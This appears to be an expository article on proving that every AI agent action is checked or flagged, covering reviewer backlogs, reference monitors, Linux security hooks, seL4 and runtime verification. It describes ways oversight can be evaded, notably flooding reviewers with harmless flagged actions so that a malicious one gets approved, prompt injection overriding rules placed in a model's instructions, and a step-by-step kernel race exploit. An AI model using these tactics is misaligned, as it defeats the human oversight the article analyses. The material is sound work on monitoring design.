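# Completeness of reporting in AI oversight: can it be proved that every action is checked or flagged?

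## What it means for every action to be checked or flagged

Reporting in AI oversight is complete if, for every action the AI system takes, either a defined procedure decides whether the action meets a stated rule or somebody receives a report that the procedure could not clear it. Complete reporting does not guarantee that the rules are wise or that the actions are harmless. The idea comes from computer security in the early 1970s, when the US Air Force wanted assurance that no program on a shared computer could reach a file without passing a check. It matters again because of AI agents, in which a language model chooses steps and carries them out through software tools.

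Suppose an agent at a small company reads files in a shared folder and sends email for the staff. *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, 2025) describes a similar agent that can also make payments and change its user's calendar. The company's one rule is that nothing from the contracts folder may go to an outside address. A small program stands between the model and the mail server. If the model attaches a contract to a message, the program compares the file's folder with the recipient's address and decides whether the rule allows the message. Sometimes the program has no basis for a decision. For example, if the agent opened a contract an hour ago and now writes to an outside address with no attachment, the message may retell the contract's terms or it may confirm a lunch. The program cannot determine which, so it holds the message and reports it to a member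 of staff.

Anything the agent does that can have an effect outside itself is an action, such as a call to the file tool or a message sent. The record of an action that the program sees is an event. The program's decision under the rule is a check, whichever way it goes: a blocked message counts as checked just as a delivered one does. The report to the staff is a flag. The property for this agent is then:

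For every action *a* in *S*: Checked(*a*) or Flagged(*a*) holds by the time *T*(*a*).

Here *S* is the scope, the set of actions that the company wants covered, and *T*(*a*) is the deadline for the action *a*. Without a deadline, nobody could show that the property had failed, since a missing flag might still arrive later. The right deadline depends on what the action does. If the agent only reads a file, the end of the day may be soon enough. For an email, the deadline is just before it is sent, because nobody can call it back. *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* (2026) classes asking a person only after an irreversible act as notification rather than control. In *Limits of Safe AI Deployment*, Manheim and Homewood (2025) similarly distinguish control, which works before or during operation and prevents failures, from oversight, which mostly comes afterwards and finds or repairs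 them. Some designs allow more time for checking by delaying the action's effect. In *Kairos* (2026), a monitor for language-model agents, a change to a file can go first to a copy that only the agent sees, and reaches the real file later if the monitor approves.

Late discovery is common enough that the deadline matters. Anthropic searched 481 million transcripts of its models' work for cases where a model had reached the open internet, and did not find an incident from January until August, according to The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts to find four models that reached the open internet*. Without the deadline *T*(*a*), the formula would count that late discovery as a success.

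### Three links

For the arrangement to be of any use in the office, three things have to hold.

- Recording: every action in scope produces an event.
- Verdict: every event receives a verdict under the rule, or a flag.
- Examination: somebody examines every flag.

"Every action is checked or flagged" means that every action is recorded and receives a verdict. It doesn't require anyone to examine the flags, but a flag that nobody reads has no effect.

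A proof about software covers the verdict link best. Because the program is a finite text, one can go through its branches and show that every event that enters it gets a verdict or a flag, even when an address is malformed or a file no longer exists. To show that the deadline is also met, the proof needs a bound on how long each branch takes and on how many events can arrive at once.

Whether every action is recorded depends on the whole installation as well as the software. One can prove that the file tool and the mail tool pass every call to the monitor, but one has to assume that the agent has no other tool, no forgotten network connection and no way to start a process that has one. This assumption is called effect exclusivity, and it means that the system can affect the world only through the mediated interface. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026), which describes a scheme for binding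 agents to commitments, states that mediation is complete only under this assumption.

If checking an action means having a person examine it, software can prove only that the case reached the reviewer, not that the reviewer examined it well. It can guarantee that a flag arrives, that the agent cannot delete it, and that the case stays open until a named person closes it. *Law at the Speed of AI* (2026) proposes a "legal interlock" that sends cases to people. The agent cannot suppress or bypass these referrals, and each approval carries the name of the person who gave it. The paper concedes that the architecture does not cover the quality of that person's judgment. Manheim and Homewood call it a veneer of human oversight when a person approves a decision that the machine has in effect already made. They add that auditing a log for past errors works only if the auditor can recognise what happened.

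Proving that the agent's actions are harmless would be a different task. For the lunch email, it would require a definition of harm, a model of the recipient, and some account of what the recipient will do with the information. Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), writing about a simpler setting in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, called preventing all unauthorised use a negative requirement, because proving it means showing that every possible threat has been foreseen. This is even harder for agents, because their makers want them to handle tasks that nobody spelled out in advance. *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (2026) concludes that nobody can list all their possible action sequences and failures. Completeness of reporting replaces the list of possible harms with a list of routes out of the system, which the people who build the system choose. Somebody must still prove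 a negative, that no further route exists, but this is a narrower question about how the system is connected.

A proof of completeness is compatible with any amount of harm. If an email leaks a contract in veiled language and the program checks and clears it, the formula is still satisfied. The program has missed a violation, and counting events would not reveal the miss.

### Flagging everything

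The formula is also easy to satisfy. A one-line program that flags every action has completeness of reporting, and so does a program that clears every action under a rule that forbids nothing. Nobody would adopt the second program, but the first is more tempting because it looks cautious.

Suppose the office has grown, and its agents now take 20,000 actions a day, of which the monitor flags 3 per cent. That makes 600 flags a day. Four reviewers work eight hours each and spend five minutes on a flag, so each handles 96 a day and the four together 384. The remaining 216 wait until tomorrow, when 600 more arrive. *Flow-by-Flow* (2026), a proposal for institutions that must review large numbers of submissions, gives the general rule. The backlog after the next period is the old backlog plus what arrives minus what the reviewers can handle, and never less than zero:

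*Q*(*t*+1) = max(0, *Q*(*t*) + *A*(*t*) − *K*)

With *A* = 600 and *K* = 384, the backlog grows by 216 flags a day. If the reviewers take flags in order of arrival, then from the third day on they read none that arrived the same day, because at least 432 older flags are already waiting and they can read only 384. After thirty days 6,480 flags are waiting, and a new one waits about 17 days for its turn. *Flow-by-Flow* uses Little's law, a theorem about queues by which the average wait equals the backlog divided by the throughput, to show that if the backlog has no bound, neither has the delay. Reading the newest flags first would help only those flags, because under any policy the reviewers can read only 64 per cent of what arrives.

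The formula still holds throughout, since every action is checked or flagged on time. The failure is entirely in the examination link. A monitor that flagged all 20,000 actions would need 209 reviewers. The office example is mild compared with industry practice. *Handoff at Frontier AI Companies* (Pistillo, Mengesha and colleagues, 2026) reports that Anthropic's monitors flag roughly 100,000 transcripts a week, of which people review about 50 after automated filtering.

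The reviewers could clear all 600 flags in the hours they have by taking 3.2 minutes over each instead of five, but *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) points out that spreading fixed attention over every case leaves less scrutiny for each one. In *Oversight Has a Capacity*, Turan (2026) estimated the effect with a simulation in which a guard program either let an agent's action through or sent it to a reviewer. The test set held 125 actions, most of them deliberately hard. The simulated reviewer made no mistakes up to a fixed number of reviews, then lost two percentage points of reliability with each further one, down to a floor of 20 per cent. With a capacity of 50 reviews, 39 per cent of the dangerous actions got through when the guard sent every action to the reviewer, compared with 22 per cent when it sent 72 per cent of them. No human reviewers took part, and the result follows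 from the assumed fatigue curve, as Turan acknowledges, so the percentages are weak evidence. The finding that flagging more actions can let more dangerous ones through is harder to dismiss, since it requires only that a reviewer gets noticeably worse when overloaded.

In Turan's model, an attacker can also exploit the overload by hiding one malicious action among harmless ones that the guard is likely to escalate. When the guard escalated 88 per cent of routine actions, 50 harmless ones were enough to get the malicious action approved 40 per cent of the time. An agent could therefore get something past the office staff without evading the monitor, by writing many harmless emails that the monitor would flag.

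One remedy is to build the reviewers' capacity into the system. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) recommends a maximum load per reviewer, beyond which the system must slow down, pause its less important agents or bring in more people. The office's agents could then take about 12,800 actions a day instead of 20,000, and 3 per cent of 12,800 is 384. A proof can cover this limit because software enforces it. But the limit reduces the agents' work by more than a third, which is presumably why it is so tempting to let the queue grow.

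### The reference monitor

The standard design for the recording and verdict links is more than fifty years old. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, Anderson (1972) examined computers that people with different security clearances had to share. A legitimate user could write a program to seize control of such a machine from inside. To prevent this, Anderson proposed the reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every reference a program makes to data, a device or another program, first comparing it with a list of what the user may do. The report set three requirements for this mechanism.

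The monitor must be tamper-proof. If the office agent can write to the folder where the monitor keeps its list of outside addresses, the agent can remove an address from the list. The monitor would still apply the list correctly, but every later verdict would be worthless because the list could be wrong.

The monitor must always be invoked. Suppose it checks all email, but calendar invitations, which also carry text and attachments, go out through another service. Contracts can then be sent in an invitation without being checked. Anderson adds that if a system suspends the check for certain programs, those programs become part of the security mechanism and must be tamper-proof and open to full analysis.

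The monitor must also be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, because otherwise they could not confirm that it meets the other two requirements.

Anderson applied the requirements to a commercial system of the time, the GCOS III operating system on a Honeywell computer. The hardware kept each user's program within its own area of memory. To read or write anything outside that area, the program called the supervisor, which mostly ran with the protection suspended, so the check was not always invoked. Even if the supervisor itself counted as the checking mechanism, it and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse. On resistance to tampering, Anderson noted only that a number of attempts to break in had succeeded.

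Saltzer and Schroeder made constant invocation a design principle, which they called complete mediation: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They included start-up, crash recovery, shutdown and maintenance, when a check can easily be missing. If the office mail server starts twenty seconds before the monitor, the agent goes unobserved for twenty seconds at every restart. They were also wary of relying on the stored results of earlier checks. If a monitor clears a law firm's address on Monday and stores the result, it will still clear the address on Thursday, after the company has dismissed the firm, unless something updates the stored result. Two of their other principles also apply. Access should require explicit permission, so that an unanticipated kind of action is refused or, in this setting, flagged. The mechanism should also be simple, because people doing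 their jobs do not look for ways around the check, so ordinary use does not reveal unwanted paths.

For AI agents, the reference monitor usually sits at the tool call. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) formalizes the cycle. The monitor suspends the call, computes the state that the call would produce, and applies the policy to that state. If the policy permits it, the tool runs and the new state becomes current. Otherwise, the monitor discards the projected state and gives the agent the reason. The monitor has to be a separate program because a rule written into the model's instructions reaches the model through the same input as the hostile text it should guard against. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), a security analysis that treats agents as operating systems, finds that such text can override the rule however carefully it is worded.

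One can partly check whether mediation is complete by counting the paths from agent to system. *Governed MCP* (2026), which describes a system that checks agents' tool calls inside the operating system, withdraws an earlier claim that all 123 paths were mediated. A new count on the running machine found 59 paths, of which 43 were mediated. Mediation was complete for the tool calls proper, but six paths for direct calls to the operating system had no gate. The property therefore held for one choice of *S* and failed for a slightly larger one, so a claim of complete mediation means little unless its scope is known.

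The Next Web's *Anthropic ran 133 million contractor chats with its bioweapon filters off* describes a larger failure, drawing on Anthropic's own risk report. From May 2025 to April 2026, the classifiers that screen for help with biological weapons did not run on traffic from the platforms through which outside contractors give feedback on models. About 50,000 people had access and produced some 133 million exchanges. A setting meant for internal use had switched off the blocking, and with it the logging. To the reviewers, it must have looked as if nothing suspicious ever happened on those platforms. Protecting the log would not have helped, because log integrity only assures that nobody has changed an entry, and these entries were never written.

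### The trusted base

Every proof of this kind concerns a mathematical description of the system. The guarantee holds in the running system only if certain things outside the proof, together called the trusted base, also work correctly. Anderson pointed out that the reference monitor concept assumes that the system can always identify its current user, that guards and locks protect the equipment, that the communication lines are safe and that the hardware works. Anderson also worried that a compiler, the program that translates source code into machine instructions, could insert a trap door (a hidden entrance that suspends the controls) into a monitor whose source code is flawless. Builders therefore had to certify the compiler or check its output independently.

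Besides the monitor, the office agent's trusted base includes the processor, the compiler, and the part of the operating system that keeps the agent's process away from the monitor's. It also includes the mail server, which must refuse any message without the monitor's approval, and the clock the monitor uses to measure the deadline. If the proof was done by machine, the proof checker is part of the base too. A fault in any of these lets the contract out, even though the theorem remains true. *Kairos* likewise argues that every channel passes through its monitor, because the monitor sits where data enters and leaves the host, but explicitly assumes that the monitor is small and tamper-proof.

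The word "complete" has several meanings. In logic, a proof system is complete if every valid statement has a proof in it, which has nothing to do with coverage of actions. People who build program analysers often call a tool sound if it misses no violation and complete if it raises no false alarm. In their terms, a monitor that flags all 20,000 actions is sound but very incomplete, because it raises a false alarm for every harmless action. Anderson's third requirement concerns the completeness of analysis and tests. In Saltzer and Schroeder's glossary, certifying a mechanism includes checking that the mechanism itself is complete.

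### Four places for a learned component

A learned component gets its behaviour from training on data, not from a written specification, so nobody can go through its branches as they can with the monitor's. How this affects the guarantee depends on where the component is in the system.

In the office, the learned component is the actor, the model that opens files and writes messages. This is the easiest case because the proof covers every request the model could make, so it needs no assumption about which requests the model will make. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* takes this approach and treats the model, the code that drives it and any process they start as the agent. The proof then depends on the barriers that confine the agent.

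The sensor or translator that produces the events can also be a learned component. Suppose contracts are not all in one folder, and a trained classifier reads each attachment and labels it "contract" or "other". Every action still produces an event, so counting events would not reveal a problem. But the classifier may label a badly scanned contract "other", and a correctly applied rule would then clear the message. Zhang and colleagues' AgentSandbox framework has a translator at this point, which converts text from outside services into a structured form before the agent acts on it. They keep the translator fixed and rule-based so that it does not change as other parts of the framework learn.

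In the third position, the learned component is the checker. *AgentBouncer* (2026) intercepts the requests that a programming agent's tools make to the operating system. A written profile decides the common requests. For the others, a language model judges whether the request is necessary for the task and whether it is safe, then answers "allow" or "deny". Every request that reaches the model therefore gets a verdict, so checks alone satisfy the formula. The error rate of these verdicts must be measured, and the measured rate may not hold against an adversary because, as *Ring-0 by Default* notes, a model used as a monitor still reads text that the agent controls.

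Finally, it matters who writes the rules. AgentSandbox contains an engine that rewrites its data-sharing policies based on how earlier tasks went, using a reward for finishing the task and protecting private data. One can still prove that a monitor applies its current policy to every event, but that policy may change from week to week. An email that it forbids in March may be permitted in April without anyone deciding to allow it. Zhang and colleagues let the learned policies adapt and put the constraints that must never change in the fixed firewall.

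## The Linux kernel: proving that no operation skips its security check

The office monitor had to watch only the mail tool, but an operating system kernel, the program that controls a computer's memory, files and devices for all other programs, has hundreds of entry points. An AI agent on a Linux machine goes through the kernel to write a file or open a network connection, so a check there applies whichever tool the agent uses. Nobody has proved that Linux makes this check every time, even though the proof would be about the kernel's source code, a fixed text with no learned component.

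### Hooks

Programs reach the kernel through system calls, which are requests such as "open this file". Linux Security Modules (LSM) is a framework that lets an administrator choose the kernel's access rules by loading a module, such as SELinux. Kernel developers write calls to the module, known as hooks, into the source code just before each sensitive operation. When a program makes a system call to move its reading position in a file, the kernel finds the file, passes it to the hook, and moves the position only if the module allows it.

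LSM places its hooks beside the operations they protect, although it would be simpler to check at the system call, where every request from a program passes. Edwards, Jaeger and Zhang (2002) explain why in *Runtime Verification of Authorization Hook Placement for the Linux Security Modules Framework*. A check at the system call uses the request's arguments, such as a file name, and the kernel looks up the object later. By then the name may lead to a different object. A hook beside the operation receives the object itself. The disadvantage is that there is no longer a single point that every operation passes through, because any kernel function may touch sensitive data.

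The developers therefore place the hooks by hand throughout the kernel. One missing hook breaks complete mediation, because even a perfect module cannot refuse an operation if the kernel never calls the module to check it.

### Unchecked until a hook has run

At IBM, Zhang, Edwards and Jaeger (2002), in *Using CQUAL for Static Analysis of Authorization Hook Placement*, turned the search for missing hooks into a problem of types. In C, the language of the kernel, every variable has a type, such as "integer" or "file", and the compiler complains if a function receives the wrong one. CQUAL is a tool that lets programmers add labels of their own to these types and reports conflicts between them. The IBM group used two labels, "unchecked" and "checked". A checked object may go wherever an unchecked one may, but a function that expects a checked object must not receive an unchecked one. In simplified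 form, the code for moving the reading position then looks like this:

```
f  = find_file(number)      // f: unchecked file
ok = hook(f)                // the security module decides
if not ok: stop
cf = f                      // cf: checked file
move_position(cf)           // accepts only a checked file
```

If a developer forgets the hook, there is no `cf`, `move_position` receives the unchecked `f`, and CQUAL reports a type error. The whole method rests on three rules:

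- A variable that holds a sensitive object starts as unchecked.
- A function that reads or writes part of such an object accepts it only as checked.
- Only a hook turns unchecked into checked.

CQUAL tracks the labels through chains of function calls. Suppose one function fetches a file and passes it to a second, which passes it to a third, which alters it. The file keeps its "unchecked" label through these calls, and CQUAL reports an error at the third function unless a hook has run on the way. CQUAL does this without running the code, so it also covers code that no test would run.

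The kernel has far too many such variables to label by hand, so the group modified the GCC compiler to list them and used scripts to write the labels into the source. CQUAL gives a variable the same label throughout a function, so `f` cannot become checked halfway down, which is why the example introduces `cf`. The scripts made a new variable after each hook and replaced the old one with it in the lines below. This is correct only if every path to those lines passes through the hook. If the hook were inside an "if" branch, the scripts would label objects as checked even when the kernel had skipped the branch. The group made a further addition to GCC to test for such cases and dealt with the few exceptions by hand.

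### What the type checker reported

The analysis of four parts of Linux 2.4.9 produced 524 type errors.

| Part of the kernel | Type errors | Errors left without "safe" functions |
|---|---|---|
| File system | 73 | 37 |
| Memory management | 18 | 14 |
| Networking | 431 | 73 |
| Communication between processes | 2 | 2 |
| Total | 524 | 126 |

Most of the errors were false alarms. Many came from functions that alter a sensitive object harmlessly, for example by counting how many programs are using it or by filling a new object with zeros. The group reviewed the functions where errors ended, marked these ones as "safe" by hand and stopped requiring a check for them, which removed 76 per cent of the errors. Somebody has to review the safe functions again with each kernel release, because if one is changed to do something that needs a check, CQUAL won't report that the check is missing.

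Some errors were hard to classify. When a program reads a file in the ordinary way, the kernel calls a hook on every read. But a program can also map the file into its memory, and then the kernel fetches the contents without calling the hook. If the administrator withdraws permission after the file is mapped, the program can still read it through the mapping, though ordinary reads fail. Nobody had written down the rule that would determine whether this was a missing check. The LSM developers left the code as it was and documented the inconsistency.

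The analysis also had gaps, so even a run with no errors would not have been a proof. When the code takes an object out of a field of a larger structure and assigns it to a checked variable, CQUAL infers that the new object is checked too, although no hook has checked it. Zhang, Edwards and Jaeger knew of this gap and had not closed it. They also left out global variables, which make up less than 2 per cent of the sensitive objects.

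An operation can need several checks, and all of them must run. To delete a file, a program needs permission to pass through the directory, to write to it and to remove entries from it, and each permission has its own hook. With only two labels, the directory would count as "checked" after any one of the three hooks had run. A separate label for each combination of hooks fixes this, but then somebody has to know which combination each operation needs.

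### The object checked and the object used

At least one of the errors was exploitable. A program can ask the kernel to lock a file, and it refers to the file by a number that it received on opening it. The kernel looked up the number and called the hook on the file it found. It then passed on the number instead of the file, and a later function looked the number up again. An attacker could use the interval:

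1. The program asks for a lock on number 5, which is its own file.
2. The kernel looks up number 5 and calls the hook, which allows the lock.
3. A second thread of the program makes number 5 refer to another file, which the program has opened only for reading.
4. The kernel looks up number 5 again and locks the other file.

The attacker can gain time for step 3 by making the kernel wait for a page of memory. As an example of the danger, the paper mentions that the Linux programs *login* and *su* try to lock a file that every user can read. Linux without LSM did not have the flaw, because its own validation came after the second lookup. The group posted a patch, and later kernels include it.

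Security researchers call this a time-of-check-to-time-of-use flaw. The hook ran and gave the correct verdict for the file it received, so counting operations and checks would not have revealed the problem. But the event described a different action from the one that took effect. The office agent could exploit the same flaw if the monitor inspected an attachment in the shared folder and the mail server then read the file again. The agent would only have to replace the file between the two reads. To prevent this, the monitor must give the mail server the same bytes it inspected.

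### Comparing runs of the kernel

The same three researchers also ran the kernel and recorded what it did. They assumed that the developers had placed most hooks correctly, so if the same operation on the same kind of data was checked differently at different times, there was probably a mistake. Their modified version of Linux 2.4.16 logged accesses to sensitive structures, together with the hooks that had run during the same system call. It sampled only one system call in twenty, because a full log would have grown faster than the disk could store it.

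One anomaly concerned a field that records which process receives signals about an open file. Two hooks ran when a program set the field directly, but only one of them ran before the kernel reset it when the program gave up a lease on the file. Another anomaly was a hook missing from an old 16-bit version of the call that sets a process's groups. Most of these old calls convert their numbers and pass them to the current version, which has the hook. This one takes an array of them, and the developers had found it easier not to convert it. The standard C library no longer offered the call, so the researchers wrote an assembly program to show that it worked. The kernel developers patched all the anomalies except the one about mapped files.

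Such a log covers only the code that ran. LMBench, one of the test programs Edwards and colleagues used, executes about 20 per cent of the kernel's code, and a missing hook in code that no test runs does not show up in the log. The log would probably not have revealed the locking flaw either, since ordinary programs do not swap files in the middle of a call. But it does record which checks each operation actually gets. The group found this hard to work out from the source code and took it from the logs when they needed requirements for CQUAL. This method judges the kernel's checks against the checks it already makes, so it works only if most of the hooks are in the right place.

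### A kernel of 15.8 million lines

By 2018 the kernel had grown to 15.8 million lines in its fullest configuration. *PeX* (Zhang, Shen and colleagues, 2019) analysed version 4.18.5 with a tool of the same name. The tool starts from 196 known permission checks, 190 of them LSM hooks, and finds 88 more functions that wrap a check. It then infers that a function is privileged if every path to a particular call to that function passes a check. Finally, it follows every path it can find from the system calls to each privileged function and reports any on which the check is missing, differs from the usual one or runs twice.

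Finding the paths is the hard part because kernel code often calls functions through pointers, so the same line can run different functions for different file systems. The full configuration has about 115,000 such calls. Matching calls to functions by type alone leaves an average of about 81,000 candidates per call. PeX also uses the kind of structure that stores the pointer, which reduces the candidates to about six. It resolves 92 per cent of the calls this way. The map may omit a path that runs through one of the other 8 per cent, in which case PeX would give no warning about it.

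PeX produced 2,088 groups of warnings. The researchers reviewed them by hand and reported 36 errors, of which kernel developers confirmed 14. The researchers suspect they missed more real errors because they lacked the developers' knowledge of the code. These warnings are also flags, and although the tool produced them in a few hours, people had to read them one by one.

One confirmed error concerned symbolic links, which are files that point to other files. The usual call for reading a link goes through a security hook, but a special command in the XFS file system called the same function without it. Some developers considered this harmless because the command already requires administrator rights. Others wanted the hook, and the researchers agreed, because LSM is supposed to limit the damage an attacker can do even after taking over an administrator's process.

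In another case, PeX reported a missing hook where the kernel loads programs. The developers answered that the hook was meant only for firmware and kernel modules. The researchers found no documentation of this, and found a place where the kernel used the same hook for other files.

### Somebody has to write the list

All these analyses depend on a hand-written list, which is the scope *S* in the formula for completeness. For CQUAL, the list contained twelve kinds of kernel object, including files, processes, sockets and shared memory. Zhang, Edwards and Jaeger assumed that programs can reach the kernel's other sensitive data only through these objects, and did not examine whether a bug might let a program bypass them. The run-time comparison logged six kinds of object and made the same assumption.

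PeX needs a list of checks but not a list of sensitive operations, because it infers which operations are sensitive from where developers have already placed checks. If no check precedes a dangerous function anywhere, PeX has no basis for classifying it as privileged. In *Automatic Placement of Authorization Hooks in the Linux Security Modules Framework*, Ganapathy, Jaeger and Jha proposed placing hooks automatically. This does not remove the problem because, according to *PeX*, such placement relies on a handwritten specification of the sensitive operations.

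### When the kernel gains a new interface

Even if the list were perfect and every operation on it had its hook, the next kernel release could undo this. Jaeger, Zhang and Edwards (2002) warned in *Maintaining the Correctness of the Linux Security Modules Framework* that changes to the kernel may unintentionally open security holes.

The largest example since then is probably io_uring, which became part of Linux in 2019. A program normally makes a system call for each operation. With io_uring, it puts its requests in a queue that it shares with the kernel, which saves time when there are many of them. The LWN article *Task-level io_uring restrictions* describes io_uring as practically an independent system-call interface. Seccomp, a common sandboxing mechanism that filters system calls, does not work with it, so some applications switch io_uring off.

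Because LSM hooks sit deep in the kernel, many of them also ran for the new requests, but coverage was incomplete. Moore posted a first set of patches, *Add LSM access controls and auditing to io_uring*, in May 2021, and that November Moore's *SELinux patches for v5.16* listed what had been missing. The kernel's audit log did not treat io_uring operations as it treated system calls, and some unusual features, such as running a request under different credentials, had no hook of their own. In the office example, this corresponds to gaps in both the recording and the verdict.

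The repair allowed exceptions, since each io_uring operation has a setting that lets it bypass the audit log. In his notes to a later version, *audit, io_uring, io-wq* (2021), Moore asks for great care in using this setting. During the discussion, somebody objected that selective auditing would make new operations more likely to go unaudited. Axboe, who maintains io_uring, agreed in *audit,io_uring,io-wq* that opening or deleting a file should leave a record, but he regarded records of ordinary reads and writes as noise.

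In 2022 the developers again left out a check when they added an io_uring operation that passes commands through to the code behind a file. This time the operation lacked a hook that would let Linux Security Modules (LSM) refuse it. Chamberlain later added the hook in *lsm, io_uring*. Axboe conceded that it should have been in the original patch series, but said that nobody Axboe knew used LSM. Schaufler (2022) replied in *lsm,io_uring* that more than six billion systems did, including every Android device.

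### seL4

The seL4 kernel has far fewer places where such accidents can happen. It is a microkernel, which means it provides little more than memory protection, processor time and messages between programs, and leaves file systems and most device drivers to ordinary programs outside the kernel. It has about 8,700 lines of C, so it comes far closer than Linux to meeting the requirement that a reference monitor be small enough to analyse.

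A program on seL4 can act on something outside itself only through a capability, a token stored by the kernel that identifies one object and specifies what the holder may do with it. To send a message, the program names one of its capabilities and the kernel looks it up. That lookup returns both the object and the permission, so there is no separate hook that a developer could forget to add.

*seL4* (Klein et al., 2009) gives a computer-checked proof that the kernel's C code does only what its specification allows. *seL4 Enforces Integrity* (Sewell et al., 2011) builds on this to prove that a program can change only what the access policy lets it change, and that programs cannot gain authority beyond the policy by passing capabilities to one another. Both results hold for every possible sequence of system calls.

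Suppose the office agent runs on seL4, its only communication capability leads to the monitor, and only the monitor has a capability for the network driver. The theorem then guarantees that the agent cannot alter the monitor's memory or gain access to the driver, whatever the model generates. This is most of what effect exclusivity requires. The theorem does not cover the monitor's own code, which needs a separate proof that every message gets a verdict or a flag.

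The proofs assume that the hardware, including the processor, memory and caches, works as modelled. Devices such as network cards can often write to memory without going through the kernel, so the proofs also assume that this access is turned off or that the device is trustworthy. The original proof also assumed that the compiler, the start-up code and about 600 lines of assembly were correct. Sewell, Myreen and Klein (2013), in *Translation Validation for a Verified OS Kernel*, later removed the need to trust the compiler by checking the machine code against the C source. The model still leaves out timing, so two programs that may not exchange messages could signal to each other by how long they keep the processor busy.

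Someone also still has to list which capabilities each program starts with. If the office mistakenly gives its agent a capability for the network driver, the theorem still holds, but the agent can send anything.

Klein and colleagues reported that designing and writing the seL4 kernel took 2.2 person-years and the proof took about 20. Eleven of those 20 went into proving seL4 itself and the rest into tools and methods, and they expected the proof for a similar kernel to take six. Changes also take work, because a new system call needs a new specification and new proofs. If a developer added an interface like io_uring to seL4 and dealt with its security two years later, the theorem would no longer cover the kernel in the meantime.

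## A rule that every request must be reviewed: what a run-time monitor can decide

On seL4, the office agent can reach only what its capabilities allow, but capabilities do not specify the order in which things must happen. Suppose the company lets the agent request payments to suppliers and adds a rule that every payment request must be followed by a review. The rule is broken only if a review never follows a request, so a program that judges each call to the payment tool separately cannot detect a violation.

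Runtime verification checks such rules on a single run of a system as it happens. A monitor reads the trace event by event and gives a verdict after each one. It needs no model of the agent's inner workings, so it works equally well for a language model and a hand-written program. However, its verdicts apply only to the run it has read.

People often write these rules in linear temporal logic, which adds a few operators about order to ordinary logic. Three of them matter here: G means "at every point from now on", F means "now or at some later point", and X means "at the next event". The office rule becomes:

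G(request → F review)

Bauer, Leucker and Schallhart gave this logic three verdicts for an unfinished run. The rule is satisfied if every possible continuation of the trace complies with it, and violated if none does. Otherwise the verdict is inconclusive.

The verdict on the office rule is always inconclusive, because any finite trace can continue in a way that satisfies the rule or in a way that violates it. If forty events have passed since a request without a review, the forty-first may be the review. After that review, the next event may be another request that nobody ever reviews.

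### Within three steps

The picture changes if the review must come within the next three events:

G(request → (X review or XX review or XXX review))

A small automaton, a machine that moves between a fixed set of states as it reads events, can now monitor the rule. It has five states. In "clear", no request is waiting for a review. In "three left", "two left" and "one left", the oldest waiting request has that many events left. The fifth state is "violated".

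A request moves the automaton from "clear" to "three left". A review moves it from any of the three waiting states back to "clear". Any other event, including a further request, uses up one of the remaining steps, and in "one left" it leads to "violated", which has no way out. Here is a run of eight events:

| Event | State afterwards | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| 1. The agent reads a file | clear | inconclusive |
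| 2. It requests payment of invoice 17 | three left | inconclusive |
| 3. It sends an email | two left | inconclusive |
| 4. Somebody does a review | clear | inconclusive |
| 5. It requests payment of invoice 18 | three left | inconclusive |
| 6. It requests payment of invoice 19 | two left | inconclusive |
| 7. It reads a file | one left | inconclusive |
| 8. It reads another file | violated | violated |

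By event 8, three events have followed the request for invoice 18 without a review, and no later event can change that. At event 4, every request had been reviewed, but the verdict was still inconclusive because a later request might not be. That possibility always remains, so this monitor can never reach the verdict "satisfied".

The automaton only has to track the oldest request because the rule lets one review settle all the requests before it. If a review had come at event 8, it would have counted for both invoices 18 and 19, even if the reviewer had looked at only one of them. To require that each request be followed by a review of the same invoice, the rule must refer to the data in the events.

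### Safety and liveness

Alpern and Schneider's standard definitions of safety and liveness separate the two versions of the rule. A rule is a safety property if every run that breaks it has a finite beginning that no continuation can repair. That is, if *P* is the set of runs that comply, then for every run σ outside *P* there is a number *i* such that every run starting with the first *i* events of σ is also outside *P*. A rule is a liveness property if every finite trace has at least one continuation that complies.

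The rule that requires a review "within three steps" is a safety property, and the eight events in the table already violate it, whatever happens next. The rule that requires a review "eventually" is a liveness property, because a review can always still come later. Completeness of reporting therefore needs the deadline *T*(*a*). Without one, the monitor would have to flag every request on arrival or wait forever.

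A monitor can reach a verdict on some liveness properties. For example, the first review settles "At some point a review takes place". Pnueli and Zaks therefore asked instead whether some finite continuation of the present trace can still settle the rule. If so, the rule is monitorable at that point. Bauer, Leucker and Schallhart showed that all safety properties are monitorable, as are all rules that hold for good once some finite trace has fulfilled them, and some rules in neither group. The office rule with "eventually" is not monitorable after any trace.

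Monitorability is still a weak assurance that every omission will be flagged. Suppose the company extends the rule to "every request is eventually reviewed, and no payment goes to a blocked account". The longer rule is monitorable because a payment to a blocked account, at any time, would show that the rule had been broken, but its monitor would never flag a missing review.

If the run is certain to end, the end can serve as the deadline. *Monitoring Data-aware Temporal Properties (Extended Version)* (Gianola, Montali and Winkler, 2026) assumes that runs end and uses four verdicts, which distinguish whether a rule holds now from whether that could still change. After a request without a review, the office rule is currently violated, and after the review it is currently satisfied. The other two verdicts, permanent violation and permanent satisfaction, apply when no continuation could change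 the result. A verdict at the end may be good enough for an agent that finishes its task in ten minutes, but if the agent runs for months, the money will have been paid out long before the verdict.

### Stopping the agent

Detecting a violation at event 8 does not prevent it. In *Enforceable Security Policies*, Schneider (2000) worked out what a monitor can enforce if it can only stop the program. Schneider's security automata resemble the one above, but they have no "violated" state. Before the program takes a step, the monitor checks whether the automaton can make a transition on that step. If it can, the step goes ahead. Otherwise the monitor terminates the program. One of Schneider's examples has two states and forbids sending messages after reading a file.

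Schneider proved that such monitors can enforce only safety properties. A monitor has no access to future events, so it cannot let a forbidden trace pass on the chance that a later event will repair it. It must also reject a bad run after a finite number of steps, but there is no step at which it can reject a run that breaks the "eventually" rule.

Under the three-step rule, the monitor would stop the agent just before event 8. The stopped run satisfies the rule only if the rule exempts runs that stop, because invoice 18 still has no review. Schneider describes the same limit for a seller who has received a payment. The automaton can forbid every action except delivery, but the seller may then do nothing.

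Some policies concern more than a single run. For example, whether an email reveals a contract's terms depends partly on what the agent would have written if the terms had been different, which a single run does not show. A monitor can only enforce a stricter rule instead, such as forbidding all email after the agent has opened a contract.

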